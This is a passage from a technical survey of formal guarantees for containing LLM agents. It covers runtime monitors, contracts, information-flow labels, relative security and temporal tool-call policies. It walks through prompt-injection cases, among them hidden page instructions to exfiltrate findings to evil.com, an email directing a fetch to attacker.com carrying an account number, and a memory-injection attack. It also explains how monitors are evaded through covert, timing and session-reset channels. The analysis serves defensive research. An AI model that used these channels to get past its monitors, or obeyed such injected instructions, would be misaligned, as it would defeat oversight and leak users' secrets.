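| GET admin.example-corp.com/ | denied | the new host is out of scope |
| POST api.example.com/login, with an attack on the database | denied | the contract does not allow POST |
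| GET evil.com/collect?data=... | denied | the host is out of scope |

The agent proposes the last request because a page on api.example.com contained hidden instructions to send all discovered vulnerabilities to evil.com. The monitor denies the request because of its host. It doesn't examine the data, since network events in this contract include neither a request's path nor its contents. An attacker who controlled api.example.com could have told the agent to put the findings in the URL of a GET request to that same server, and the monitor would have allowed it unless some other component had declared the disclosure.

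Let Run_C(*p*) be the trace that remains after the monitor for contract *C* goes through a finite list *p* of proposed events and removes the inadmissible ones. By the enforcement soundness theorem, Run_C(*p*) satisfies *C* for every *p*. The proof is by induction on *p*. A denial leaves the trace unchanged, and an approval adds an event that has just passed the monitor's test. David and colleagues checked this proof in Lean 4. Because the theorem holds for every finite list, it also covers models that react to what they read, as with the file agent.

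This induction needs no separate invariant about a counter, because the monitor in the theorem recomputes the sum of all past costs at every event. A practical monitor would keep running totals, so that the time for each check doesn't depend on the length of the trace. Its proof would again need an invariant like the file agent's, stating that each total equals the sum over the trace.

The theorem is also short because the monitor's test and the definition of a satisfactory trace use the same predicate. An error in that predicate would affect both, so the proof would still be valid. According to *Developing Theoretical Foundations for Runtime Enforcement*, the classical work by Schneider and by Ligatti and colleagues also lacks a clear separation between specification and mechanism. The contract paper excludes mistakes in the contract from its guarantee and assumes that every relevant effect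 reaches the monitor as a correct event. It also proves rules for tightening and combining contracts.

### What the monitor cannot observe

David and colleagues also ask which policies a monitor could enforce in principle if it observes only part of each event, written obs(*e*). Suppose that the policy permits one trace and forbids another, but obs gives the same sequence of observations for both. A transparent monitor must allow every event of the permitted trace. Because its decisions depend only on what it observes, it also allows every event of the forbidden trace, so it is not sound. The file agent's monitor does not read message bodies, so it could not enforce a rule against posting the keys without also blocking harmless posts. Blocking all posts would enforce the rule, but the monitor would then not be transparent.

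Their "enforcement boundary" theorem goes further and states that a blocking monitor can enforce a policy, soundly and transparently, exactly when the policy depends only on observable features and every violation has a finite bad prefix. However, the theorem assumes each direction of this equivalence separately, and the Lean proof only combines the two assumptions. David and colleagues acknowledge this and call the result a schema. The argument above proves part of one direction, and the rest must still be proved for each monitor.

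The related proposition on bad prefixes is also weaker than its name suggests. It states that every finite trace that violates a contract has a prefix that violates it, which is true of any policy because a trace is a prefix of itself. Contracts do have the property that matters, which is that later events cannot undo a violation. This follows from the definition of satisfaction, under which a single inadmissible event makes a trace violate the contract.

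The boundary leaves out several things an operator might care about. The monitor cannot detect information hidden in the body of a permitted message. Delays between events can also carry information, and although the monitor observes the time of each event, the contract language cannot restrict timing patterns. The monitor also cannot distinguish a malicious model from a benign one if both produce the same events.

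### Invariants on states

Sterling proves a theorem about the states of Agentic Redux rather than its traces. In this design, sub-agents propose changes and a single meta-agent decides on them. The operator supplies a list of invariants, each of which can be checked on a single state of the system. For each proposal, the meta-agent computes the resulting state and commits it only if it satisfies every invariant. Otherwise, the meta-agent rejects the proposal or refers it to a person.

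One of Sterling's applications is billing for drug tests in Arizona. A patient who has been abstinent for more than 90 days may have up to three detailed tests in 90 days, but after a relapse the limit changes to one in seven days. Suppose the patient has a negative detailed test, and three days later a quick test detects opioids. A second detailed test that day is no longer covered. A billing agent with out-of-date records would approve it, but the meta-agent checks the claim against the current state.

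The invariant preservation theorem applies to every program that uses the design correctly and every oracle trace (the model's answers and the scheduling decisions). If the starting state satisfies all the invariants, so does every state the system can reach. The proof is again by induction. Every step except an approval leaves the state unchanged, and an approval installs only a state that has passed the tests. The theorem directly rules out write skew, the error in which two agents jointly overspend a shared budget.

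Because the meta-agent checks the new state instead of the action, the theorem holds even if the code that computes that state contains errors. However, an invariant can refer only to a single state, not to the proposed action or the previous state, so a rule such as "the balance may fall by at most $100 per step" requires the state to record the earlier balance.

The file agent's third clause is a rule about past events, which would become *n* ≤ 2 as a state invariant. Suppose a programmer forgets to increase *n* after a post. Then *n* stays at 0, every state satisfies the invariant and the invariant preservation theorem remains true, even though the agent can send any number of messages. The proof in this section would fail because it requires *n* to equal the number of Sent events. Any safety property can become a state invariant if the state contains enough of the history, but someone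 must then show that the recorded history matches what happened.

*Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) also defines safety in terms of states. Its barrier rejects any action whose resulting state would break a fixed set of axioms. The paper assumes that the current state and the action together determine the resulting state. This assumption holds for a ledger, which the runtime controls, but is less realistic for a network request, whose outcome depends on other machines.

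Sterling's audit log theorem does concern the past. It states that each decision adds exactly one entry to the log, no other step adds any, and no step alters an existing entry. Another result, agent confinement, states that a sub-agent's proposal depends only on its own part of the state and on the oracle trace, and that calling a sub-agent changes nothing. This follows from the definition of an agent as a function of that part of the state, so in practice it holds only if the tools read nothing else.

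In the version with human review, the reviewer can commit a state that breaks the invariants, so the guarantee holds only if no reviewer does. Sterling also reports that a language model generated about 90 per cent of the appendix containing the proofs, and that he found errors in earlier versions. The main induction is simple enough to check by hand, but the longer proofs would benefit from a proof checker.

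### The objection from computability

*Superintelligence cannot be contained* (Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues, 2016; published in a journal in 2021) argues that containment is impossible in principle. It considers a program R that takes the state of the world D as input and can simulate any other program. The paper defines R as containable if some control strategy stops it from acting whenever R(D) would harm humans and allows it to act otherwise. Such a strategy has to decide whether R(D) will cause harm.

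No algorithm can decide, for every program and input, whether the program will cause harm. The proof uses the halting problem. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no algorithm can determine, for every program T and input I, whether T eventually stops on I. Suppose a program HaltHarm(T, I) first runs T on I in isolation and then, if T stops, does something harmful. HaltHarm causes harm exactly when T stops on I, so an algorithm that could always predict harm would solve the halting problem, which is impossible.

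The proof is correct, but it concerns a different task from the monitor's. Suppose HaltHarm replaces the model in the file agent, and the harmful act is a post to files.example.net. While T runs, even if it never stops, HaltHarm proposes nothing and the monitor has nothing to decide. If T stops, HaltHarm proposes the post, and the monitor compares the host with api.example.org and denies it. The monitor never has to determine whether T will stop. David and colleagues prove a corresponding result for contracts, that a program can decide whether one proposed event is admissible as long as it can evaluate each of the contract's tests.

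The definition of "containable" is also stricter than soundness, because it requires the strategy to allow every harmless run. The theorem does not rule out a monitor that denies every action, which would prevent all harm that depends on the program's actions. Alfonseca and colleagues reasonably object that complete isolation would give up the system's benefits, but this objection concerns usefulness. A monitor can exactly enforce many policies that lie between complete isolation and perfect prediction of harm.

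Alfonseca and colleagues grant that formal verification works for restricted classes of programs, such as those for scheduling trains, but consider it useless for a superintelligence, which would need to run arbitrary programs and take the whole world as input. A containment proof restricts the system's effects and leaves the model itself unrestricted. The file agent's theorem holds for an oracle of any intelligence, even one that no computer could implement. But a superintelligence limited to two messages to one host would probably not end an epidemic. Part of the objection therefore still holds, because the more a system needs to do, the harder it is to write a policy that is both permissive enough and protective.

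The theorem also does not imply that any particular system is unsafe. Undecidability means that no single method gives the right answer for every program, but a given program may still be safe, and someone may be able to prove it. Wu and colleagues are therefore wrong to infer from the undecidability of model behaviour that an unprotected agent under attack can certainly reach a forbidden state.

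### Where undecidability returns

A policy can bring back the halting problem if it depends on a program's future behaviour. Suppose the file agent's policy had a fourth clause allowing it to post only scripts that eventually stop. This is still a safety property, since posting a script that runs for ever violates the clause immediately and irreversibly. But no monitor can always recognise the violation, so the policy fails Ray's requirement that the monitor can compute whether a trace has violated the policy. A clause against posting any program that would harm someone has the same problem. A workable policy has to use a cautious substitute, such as a list of approved scripts.

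Analysing the policy itself can be undecidable too. Ray shows that no algorithm can always tell whether a policy will ever forbid anything if the policy language has two counters that can go up and down and rules that can test them for zero. Such a policy is still easy to enforce, because the monitor only updates the counters after each event. The file agent's *n* only goes up, and the monitor compares it with a constant. Ray proves that the question is decidable for a class of policies with counters of this kind.

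New tools are probably the most important case for agents. An agent may download or write a program, and an operator might want to certify, before the program runs, that it will never attempt a forbidden effect. David and colleagues explain why no method can do this for all tools. Given any program M and input *x*, one can build a tool that ignores its own input, simulates M on *x* and attempts a forbidden effect if M halts. The tool attempts no forbidden effect if and only if M runs forever on *x*, so a perfect certifier would solve the halting problem. This is the same construction as HaltHarm. Lean checks only the general step, that an undecidable question remains undecidable when translated into a question about tools, while the construction of the tool is argued in prose.

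An operator can use a cautious certifier, which never approves a dangerous tool but rejects some harmless ones. For example, it might reject every tool whose code contains a network call that it cannot trace to a permitted host. Alternatively, the operator can run an uncertified tool in a sandbox that sends each of its effects to the monitor. The monitor allows or blocks each effect, as it does for the model's proposals.

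## Proving that information does not leave

The file agent's containment theorem does not rule out the model posting the contents of /work/keys.txt to api.example.org. The operator wants the messages not to depend on the key at all. A fourth clause against posting the file's contents would not guarantee this. The monitor could compare every message with the file and deny any match, but the model could still post the key backwards or with one added to every digit, or post "yes" if the first digit is even and "no" if it is odd. No list of forbidden texts covers every such encoding.

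### Comparing two runs

Goguen and Meseguer made this requirement precise in 1982 and called it noninterference: what an observer sees must not depend on secret inputs. For the file agent, the secret is the content of keys.txt and the observer is whoever controls api.example.org. Let Sent(S, r, w, k) be the sequence of Sent events in the first *k* steps of a run with strategy S, request *r* and starting world *w*. Noninterference then requires:

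```
For every strategy S, every request r, every number of steps k,
and all worlds w1 and w2 that differ only in the contents of keys.txt:
    Sent(S, r, w1, k) = Sent(S, r, w2, k).
```

Because S is a strategy and not an unconstrained oracle, the same model takes part in both runs. The file agent fails the test because a strategy that reads keys.txt and posts the file's first digit sends "3" in one world and "7" in the other.

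One way to meet the requirement is to deny every read of keys.txt. The proof compares the two runs step by step, like the proof of Reasoning Integrity for PerMIT. Its invariant is that the two histories are equal, the two counts are equal and the two worlds still differ only in keys.txt. Each step preserves this invariant because no reply contains the key.

A milder change allows the read but denies every post after it. The two runs are identical until the model reads the file, so they reach that point at the same step, and neither sends anything afterward. However, this also prevents the agent from posting a harmless summary after reading the key.

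A test that examines one run at a time cannot express noninterference. Suppose the key is one bit, and three agents each post one bit. Agent A posts the key, agent B always posts 0, and agent C always posts 1. B and C satisfy noninterference, so a test that expresses it must accept all their runs. But A's run is identical to B's when the key is 0, and to C's when the key is 1. The test therefore accepts both of A's runs, although A leaks the whole key.

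Clarkson and Schneider introduced the term hyperproperty for a requirement on the set of all runs a system can produce. A monitor observes only the current run, so it has to enforce a stricter rule that applies to single runs and implies the hyperproperty, such as "No posts after reading keys.txt". This rule also blocks a model like C that reads the key and then posts 1 whatever the key is.

### Labels that follow the data

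That rule treats everything the agent does after the read as secret. A finer method labels each value and derives the labels of new values from those of the old ones. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) builds labels from two marks, U for untrusted and S for secret. A value computed from two others gets all the marks of both. If notes.txt carries U and keys.txt carries S, a sentence that draws on both files carries U and S, and a check before Post can refuse any body marked S.

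A program can also reveal information about a secret through the branch it takes. If it posts "yes" when the key is even and "no" otherwise, it sends only public constants, but anyone who reads the message learns whether the key is even. The runtime therefore also keeps a label for the current point in the program. Inside a branch that depends on a secret, this label contains S, and the runtime adds the label to every value computed there.

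Garby and colleagues build these rules into a small language for writing agents, an extension of the lambda calculus (a minimal programming language in which everything is a function). Its operator @ calls the model. To evaluate @*e*, the runtime computes the value of *e*, turns it into text, sends it to the model with the conversation so far, and parses the response into a value or code. The response and the extended conversation both receive the combined marks of the prompt and the earlier conversation. One untrusted email in a conversation therefore marks every later response from the model. To avoid this, a program can fork the conversation, clear the copy, send the untrusted text to the model there, and return to the original.

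Later calls can read the conversation, so the language stops with an error whenever a branch that depends on a secret tries to add to a public conversation. Marking the conversation S whenever a secret influences a prompt would not be enough. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, a program prompts the model to remember that x is false, then prompts it to set x to true if a secret is true, and finally asks for x. If the secret is true, the answer is marked S, as it should be. If the secret is false, the program skips the second prompt, so the conversation stays public and the answer "false" reveals the secret without being marked.

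But whether this error occurs also depends on the secret, since the program stops if the secret is true and finishes if it is false. The noninterference theorem allows this. It compares two programs that differ only in parts whose labels the observer may not see. If both programs finish, the observer cannot distinguish their results or their final conversations. The theorem does not apply if either program stops with an error or runs forever. Such theorems are called termination-insensitive.

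An observer who learns only whether a single run finished gains at most one bit. An agent that sends messages as it works can reveal more. For example, it could post 0, then 1, then 2, and get stuck when it reaches the first digit of the key. Sands and three co-authors made this point in a 2008 paper, using the title to state that guarantees that ignore whether a run finishes leak "more than just a bit". The LLMbda theorem compares final results and conversations, so an agent that posts messages while it runs needs a further argument.

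The theorem also restricts how programs may test labels, because a label can itself depend on a secret. A program that enforces a policy has to test whether a value is secret and use the answer in public. Suppose a value marked "middle" contains another value marked "high" in one run but not in the other. An observer at the "low" level may not see either value, but the public answer to "is this at most middle?" differs between the runs. The theorem therefore covers programs that never test labels, programs that use only one label besides "public and trusted", and programs that test labels only in two safe ways. The safe ways are an assertion, which prevents the program from finishing if it fails, and a test whose answer carries the label it tests for.

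Garby and colleagues prove all this by hand. They assume that the model's response is a fixed function of the conversation, and leave random responses to future work. They also place all data inside the program, so the theorem does not yet cover tools that fetch data from elsewhere.

### FIDES and CaMeL

The same labels can protect the agent's actions from untrusted text. In a demonstration by Garby and colleagues, a user asks an agent to send a meeting reminder to the sender of the last email. The email contains planted text claiming that the meeting is off. An ordinary agent, which reads the email in the same conversation as its instructions, sends a cancellation.

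In the safer version, the model writes a short program, including the reminder's subject and body, before anything reads the email. The program passes the email to a separate, quarantined model call that returns only the sender's address. The function that sends mail asserts that the subject and body do not carry U, so by the theorem no change to the email can alter them in a run that finishes. The address does carry U, but the function does not check it, so a hostile email might still redirect the reminder to someone else.

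This example and its defence come from CaMeL, a system that Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025. CaMeL's interpreter gives each value tags, called capabilities, that record how the value came about, and it checks a policy before each tool call. The paper gives no proof of security and leaves formalisation to later work.

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues published in the same year, labels messages and tool results by trust and confidentiality. They prove noninterference for integrity and explicit secrecy for confidentiality, both for one particular agent loop. Explicit secrecy is weaker than noninterference because it ignores leaks through a program's choices. Garby and colleagues doubt that it is worth much in a language like theirs, where programs can leak information this way very efficiently.

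Dongol gives an example of such a leak in an agent with CaMeL-style tags. The agent asks a quarantined model a question about the user's private notes and an email, then sends 1 or 0 depending on the answer. Both numbers are public constants, so both pass the tag check. An injected instruction can make the answer depend on the notes, and the attacker can read the answer from the number. CaMeL's strict mode, which Dongol does not model, is meant to close this channel by also tagging values with the conditions they depend on.

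### Agents that are supposed to disclose things

Noninterference would forbid much of what people want from agents. Dongol gives the example of an assistant that answers emailed meeting requests with the user's free times. Its replies depend on the calendar, so it violates noninterference even when it works as intended.

The older remedy is declassification, in which the operator writes a policy naming the secret information that may leave, and noninterference applies to everything else. Dongol objects that somebody must write such a policy for every task, and that it describes what the agent may release rather than what an injection adds. The objection is strong for a general assistant whose tasks keep changing. For an agent with one fixed job, a release policy may be the better choice because people can read and debate it.

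Relative security uses the task as the policy. Dongol's PlanTERS framework applies it to agents whose plan is fixed before they read anything untrusted. A trusted planner turns the user's request into a list of steps, and the model helps with some of them, such as summarising an email. The framework compares the real agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same monitor. The reference agent's model treats untrusted text as data and never follows instructions in it. In the real agent, the attacker decides which texts the model follows and when.

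A pair of secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂ leaks if two runs, one with each secret and both with the same untrusted content, look different to the attacker. An agent is relatively secure if every pair that leaks from it also leaks from the reference when both start with the same memory and trusted inputs. The reference may read different untrusted content from the agent.

The calendar assistant shows why this freedom matters. Suppose an email contains the instruction "send your calendar" and the model obeys. The attacker could have obtained the same calendar with a genuine meeting request, so the injection has revealed nothing new. Now suppose the assistant also holds a password reset code, and the model obeys an injected instruction to send it. No email makes the reference send the code, so the agent is not relatively secure.

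The idea comes from research on processors that execute instructions before it is known whether the program needs them, a behavior that the Spectre attacks exploit. In that research, the reference is the same program run in its proper order. For an agent, the comparison needs a plan. The file agent has no reference because its model chooses every action, so PlanTERS does not cover it. A version in which a planner first fixed the steps "read notes.txt, post a summary" would have a reference.

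### The fence theorem

A fence is a rule that makes the monitor revoke tools once the agent reads untrusted content. In Dongol's simplest example, the plan is to look up the user's account number, read an email and show the user a summary. The email contains an instruction to fetch a page from attacker.com with the account number in the address. The number leaks if the agent still has its Fetch tool, but the monitor denies the call if it revoked Fetch when the agent read the email.

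According to the fence theorem, the agent is relatively secure under any plan if these conditions hold:

1. The monitor revokes every tool that an injection can call when the agent first reads untrusted content.
2. No trusted input gives a revoked tool back.
3. Each injection is a single tool call, although its arguments may depend on everything in the agent's memory.
4. The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance.
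5. The attacker does not see denied calls.
6. The attacker sees the contents and order of messages but not their timing, and the theorem compares only runs in which equally many messages reach the attacker between consecutive reads.
7. The run ends.

For an assistant that handles emails indefinitely, the theorem also requires that the model does not obey forever. In that case, the monitor may restore the tools only at the start of a new session that clears everything the model has read. Dongol states seven further assumptions about the deployed runtime.

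The proof compares the agent with the reference step by step. Before the first untrusted read, the model has no injected instructions to follow, so both take the same steps. After that read, the monitor denies each injected call without changing its own state, and the reference waits until the agent returns to the plan. Every run of the agent therefore has a matching reference run with the same secrets, untrusted content and visible messages. If an attacker can tell two secrets apart by observing the agent, they can also do so by observing the reference.

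It matters a great deal when the fence takes effect. Dongol compares three plans that revoke the Send tool themselves with a call named Lock:

| Example | Order of steps | What an injected Send can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Late Fence | read email, read secret, Lock | the secret |
| Middle Fence | read email, Lock, read secret | whatever was already in memory |
| Early Fence | Lock before reading the email | nothing |

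A fence also prevents the plan from using the tool. If the task is to answer the email, a fence on Send prevents the answer. Relative security does not measure this loss because the reference runs under the same monitor, so a monitor that denies every call is relatively secure. Removing a tool can also make an agent lose relative security. Suppose the plan is designed to send a secret to the attacker through Send, and an injection sends it through Fetch. The agent is relatively secure because the reference leaks the secret too. If the operator revokes only Send, the reference stops leaking the secret, and the injected Fetch becomes a violation.

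User approval lets the agent keep using a tool after reading untrusted text. If the user approves the next use of Send in general, an injection can use up that approval to send private data before the plan sends the approved reply. But if the user approves the exact message, the monitor allows an injected call only when it would send that same message, so an attacker who sees only the messages learns nothing new.

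Exact approval is secure against an attacker who sees only events, but one who also sees the step at which each message leaves can learn whether a secret equals the approved reply. Suppose the injection makes the agent try to send a secret *s*. If *s* differs from the approved reply, the monitor denies the call and the reply leaves at its planned step. If *s* equals the reply, the monitor allows the call and the message leaves one step earlier.

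Dongol judges 25 small agents in this way. Ten are secure, nine leak, and the verdict on the other six depends on what the attacker sees or on a further assumption. Most of the "secure" verdicts cover only the injection in the example, whereas the fence theorem covers all injections that meet its conditions. One of the six conditional verdicts is for spotlighting, which marks untrusted text and instructs the model not to obey it. Spotlighting works if the model follows that instruction, which no proof about the runtime can establish.

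The whole development is about 31,600 lines of Isabelle in 89 files. Dongol produced the theorems and proofs with the help of Claude Code, a coding agent. Isabelle checked every proof, and people compared the definitions and theorems with those in the paper.

Dongol also applies the theorem to reported attacks. In SpAIware, a web page made ChatGPT store an instruction in its long-term memory. In later conversations, ChatGPT loaded the instruction and sent the user's messages to the attacker. A fence that restores the agent's tools at each new session stops this attack only if it counts loading the memory as an untrusted read.

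### A full disclosure that counts as secure

Relative security depends on whether the attacker could have distinguished two secrets with some input, not on how much the attacker learns from one input. Dongol gives an example that shows how large this difference can be. The plan reads a guess from the attacker and reports whether it equals a secret *s*, but an injection makes the agent send *s* itself.

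The agent is relatively secure because every pair of different secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂ already leaks from the reference, which distinguishes them if the attacker guesses *s*₁. Yet the injected agent is far less secure in practice. If *s* is a four-digit code, an attacker with one guess succeeds once in 10,000 attempts against the reference and every time against the injected agent.

Dongol's stricter version, uniform relative security, requires the reference's untrusted input to depend only on the attacker's input to the real agent, not on the secrets. In the example, the guess must therefore be the same whatever the secret is. The reference then gives the same reply for any two secrets that both differ from the guess, but the injected agent's replies distinguish them, so the agent does not satisfy uniform relative security. The fence theorem also implies the uniform version, because each run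 of the agent matches a reference run with the same untrusted content.

### Attacks that change what the agent does

An injection can do harm without revealing anything, for instance by ordering a payment. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (Dongol, 2026) covers such attacks by extending the comparison with a reference. Relative integrity concerns the sequence of a run's trusted inputs and effects. If two runs with the same trusted inputs produce different sequences, the reference must be able to produce both, possibly after reading different untrusted content.

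Suppose the user asks an agent to pay the invoice in Bob's latest email. If the email also says to pay Mallory £1,000 and the agent obeys, it makes two payments. The reference never pays twice, so the agent violates relative integrity. It also violates it by obeying an instruction to delete the email. But if the email says "change the payee to Mallory" and the agent obeys, relative integrity still holds, because the reference would have paid Mallory if the invoice had named her. The user loses the money even though the property holds. The plan pays whomever the invoice names, so the operator would have to add a check to it, such as a list of known payees.

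An agent that pays Mallory whatever the emails contain also satisfies relative integrity. The property restricts only behaviour that varies while the trusted inputs stay the same, so this counts as an ordinary bug.

A system can satisfy confidentiality and integrity separately and still allow an attack, because each property may rely on a different run of the reference. Relative robustness requires the same reference runs to reproduce both the leak and the effects. Dongol illustrates the difference with Tensor Trust, an online game in which players protect accounts with a prompt that contains an access code. The text "[correct password]" opened 43 accounts that used 36 different codes, because the model accepted it in place of the code.

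Dongol put an invented secret record behind each of 43 accounts and replayed the game's recorded answers. The resulting gate passes relative security, since an attacker can already test a guessed code against the reference. It passes relative integrity, since somebody with the right code would receive the same record. It fails relative robustness, because no single input obtains all 43 records from the reference. Ordinary program code that compares the input with the stored code fixes the gate. The accounts are selected cases, so they can't be used to estimate how common the weakness is.

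The table lists verdicts for several example agents, one for each defence.

| Defence | Relative security | Relative integrity | Relative robustness |
|---|---|---|---|
| Revoke tools at the first untrusted read | yes | yes | yes |
| Revoke them after that read | no | no | no |
| Allow-list of web addresses | yes | no | no |
| Quarantined model without tags | no | yes | no |
| Quarantined model with tags | yes | yes | yes |
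| User approves the tool | no | no | no |
| User approves the exact message | yes | yes | yes |
| Model checks the access code | yes | yes | no |

The allow-list fails on integrity because an injection can still trigger a permitted fetch that is not in the plan. The tagged version of the quarantined model passes partly because it refuses even the honest reply. The verdict on exact approval again assumes that the observer cannot time the messages and that the model does not obey forever.

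The fence theorem carries over to all three properties under the same conditions. In practice, however, a fence can still block legitimate actions. In a banking task where a bill contains an instruction to pay the attacker, a fence on payments blocks both the attack and the payment of the bill. Allowing payments to a list of known billers lets the agent pay the bill, but does not prevent an injected instruction from making it pay one of those billers twice.

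### Timing and other hidden channels

All these theorems cover only what the semantics records, and an attacker may observe more. The LLMbda theorem does not cover whether a program finishes or how long it takes. Both of Dongol's papers exclude side channels, meaning physical traces of a computation such as its running time or its use of shared hardware. The work on integrity also leaves out the timing of effects.

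The event-level definition in PlanTERS can miss a leak through the number of messages. Suppose an injection fetches a permitted page if a secret is 0 and a forbidden page otherwise, and the plan then sends a fixed completion message. The attacker receives two messages in one case and one in the other. The definition compares only runs in which the attacker receives the same number of messages between reads, so it does not compare these two runs and does not count the difference as a leak.

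The step-level definition detects this channel, but it compares only runs of equal length. If the secret decides whether the agent takes an extra step, the definition never compares the runs with different secrets, so it misses even an injection that openly sends a bit of the secret. At this level, the fence theorem also requires that the plan's choices not depend on secrets. Steps in the semantics have no duration, so a proof that counts steps would not show that a real model call may take longer on a longer secret.

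If a channel cannot be proved closed, a limit on its capacity would still help. An observer who can see *N* different outcomes learns at most log₂ *N* bits from a session. Suppose the file agent may post only sentences from a fixed list of 16. With at most two posts, an observer without a clock can see 1 + 16 + 16² = 273 outcomes, so a session leaks at most about 8.1 bits. A random 256-bit key would take at least 32 sessions to leak.

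If each session lasts a minute, the runtime sends at most one message per second, and the observer knows in which second each message arrives, the number of outcomes rises to 1 + 16 × 60 + 16² × 1,770 = 454,081, where 1,770 is the number of ways to choose two of the 60 seconds. The limit is about 18.8 bits per session, so 14 sessions could be enough to reveal the key. If the agent may write its own text, one message can hold the entire key, and no useful limit exists.

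A proof of such a limit would need a semantics that includes everything the observer can see, with times as precise as the observer can measure. The runtime would have to keep the number of possible outcomes small, for example by holding all messages until a fixed moment at the end of the session, which would bring the count back to 273. The operator would also need to limit the total information revealed across sessions, because an attacker can combine what each one reveals. The count would still leave out other covert channels, such as the load on a shared machine.

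## Writing the policy and checking what it says

A containment theorem guarantees that the runtime enforces the policy someone wrote, which may not be the policy they wanted. *ToolGuardian* (2026), a design that vets agents' tools with logical rules, notes that "determinism is not the same as correctness". A monitor with a wrong rule makes the same mistake every time.

### Forms of policy

Most rules for agents take one of four forms, which differ in how much the monitor has to remember.

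| Form | Example for the file agent | What the monitor must remember |
|---|---|---|
| Allowlist | Post only to api.example.org | nothing |
| Budget | Post at most twice | a running total |
| Rule over past events | No post after reading keys.txt | whether the read has happened |
| Rule over data labels | Post no text marked S (secret) | the label of every value |

A rule can also call for a response other than denying an action. In *Customizable Runtime Enforcement for Safe and Reliable LLM Agents* (2025), each rule consists of a triggering event, a condition and a response, such as asking the user for confirmation.

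With the history rule as a fourth clause, the file agent's policy is this predicate on a trace *t*:

```
P(t) holds if, for all positions i and j in t:
  1.  if t[i] = FileRead(path), then path lies under /work
  2.  if t[i] = Sent(host, body), then host = api.example.org
  3.  t contains at most two Sent events
  4.  if t[i] = FileRead(/work/keys.txt) and i < j, then t[j] is not a Sent event
```

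To enforce the fourth clause, the monitor needs one more bit, *r*, which starts at 0 and becomes 1 when the monitor allows a read of keys.txt. The rule for an allowed post gets the extra condition *r* = 0. The invariant in the containment proof gets the extra condition that *r* is 1 exactly when *t* contains FileRead(/work/keys.txt). The same induction still works.

A rule over labels would take more work, because a Sent event contains only a host and a body. The runtime would have to track labels and add the body's label to the event. Similarly, if a disclosure rule in David and colleagues' contracts depends on where data came from, another component must add that information to the event before the monitor tests it.

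### Tightening and combining contracts

An agent that tests a client's web servers may have to follow the client's letter, its own firm's rules and the law, which different people may maintain. David and colleagues prove two theorems about such overlapping contracts, both checked in Lean.

The first theorem concerns refinement. A contract C′ refines a contract C if C′ has the same or a narrower scope, allows no additional kinds of event, forbids everything that C forbids, sets no larger budgets and permits no additional disclosures. C′ must also check every resource that C checks, and the two contracts must calculate costs and disclosures in the same way. By this theorem, every trace that satisfies C′ also satisfies C. The proof shows that passing each of the five tests under C′ implies passing the corresponding test under C. For a budget, the total cost is at most B′(*r*), which is at most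 B(*r*).

A firm can therefore compare a new client contract with its general rules once, before the agent runs. For example, the file agent's contract with a budget of one post refines the same contract with a budget of two. The comparison can fail even when the new contract is stricter. Suppose C allows GET and POST but also explicitly forbids POST, while C′ allows only GET. Every trace that satisfies C′ satisfies C, but C′ is not a refinement because it doesn't list POST among the forbidden events. Adding that redundant prohibition to C′ makes it a refinement.

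The second theorem is that a trace satisfying the composition of two contracts, C₁ and C₂, satisfies both contracts if they are compatible. The composition permits only targets, events and disclosures that both contracts permit, forbids whatever either forbids, and uses the smaller of the two budgets for each resource. However, it takes three components from C₁ alone: the list of resources to check, the cost function and the function that extracts disclosures. David and colleagues call the contracts compatible when these three components are the same in both.

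The file agent shows what happens without it. Let C₁ contain the rules about paths and hosts and track no resources. Let C₂ contain the same rules and a budget of two posts. The composition keeps the limit of two posts but inherits the empty resource list from C₁, so the limit is never checked. A trace with three posts to api.example.org therefore satisfies the composition but violates C₂.

In the opposite order, the composition does check posts, so the budget holds. But a contract assigns a number even to resources it doesn't track. If C₁ assigns 0 to posts, the smaller budget is 0 and the agent can't post at all. The operator can avoid both problems by making the contracts track the same resources, or by running a separate monitor for each contract and letting an event happen only if both monitors allow it.

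David and colleagues prove that a trace satisfying the composition of two contracts satisfies both contracts, but they don't prove the converse. The converse also seems to follow from the definitions if the contracts are compatible, so combining them should not block anything that both would allow.

### History rules in practice: Dogwood

In 2026 AWS, Amazon's cloud-computing business, released Dogwood, an open-source policy language for agents' tool calls. It extends Cedar, an AWS language that evaluates one request at a time, by letting rules depend on earlier events. AWS uses Dogwood in Policy in AgentCore, a service that checks tool calls outside the model. According to AWS's *Temporal policies*, the service allows a call only if a "permit" rule applies and no "forbid" rule does.

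The service records a *request* event when it authorises a call, a *response* event when the tool returns successfully, and an *error* event when a policy denies the call or the tool fails. A rule can ask whether a matching event occurred within a time window or whether a condition has held since some event. It can also count events or add up one of their fields. With shortened tool names, the file agent's fourth clause would look roughly like this:

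```
forbid (principal, action == Post, resource)
when temporal {
    formerly within 24h Read::request{
        eventResource: resource, input.path: "/work/keys.txt" }
};
```

The rule matches the request because the service records a response shortly after the call completes. A rule that matched the response could miss a post sent before that record appears, when the model already has the key. The time window is also a compromise, because AWS allows at most 24 hours per condition. In a session longer than a day, the agent could read the key, wait until the window had passed and then post it.

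AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* documents rules for an agent that transfers money, including these:

| Rule | Allowed | Denied |
|---|---|---|
| Transfer only to an account looked up in the past hour | look up account A, transfer to A | look up A, transfer to B |
| One transfer per approval | approval, transfer, new approval, transfer | approval, transfer, second transfer |
| Total transfers in five minutes must stay below 3,000 | two transfers of 1,000 | a third transfer of 1,000 |
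| One minute between transfers | transfer, wait more than a minute, transfer | two transfers within a minute |

The choice between request and response is easy to get wrong. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) recounts an example from AWS's announcement, in which an agent with a cap of $5,000 starts three transfers of $2,000 at once. A rule that adds up responses allows all three, for a total of $6,000, because no transfer has finished when the rule is checked, whereas a rule that adds up requests denies the third. For the one-minute pause, requests are the wrong choice because the history already includes the request being checked. A rule against transferring within a minute of another request would match that same request and forbid every transfer.

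The rule for one transfer per approval uses responses for the same reason, and it seems to have the same weakness as the faulty cap. It permits a transfer if no transfer has finished since the last approval, so two transfers sent at the same moment would both pass unless something else makes one wait for the other. AWS advises developers to let one call finish before sending another that depends on it, but a model under an attacker's influence might not follow this advice.

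History is also kept separately for each session, and the caller supplies the session's identifier. AWS warns that a caller can reset a rate limit by starting a new session, so the limit won't stop a determined caller. For the file agent, "at most twice" would hold per session only if trusted code, not the model, chose the identifier.

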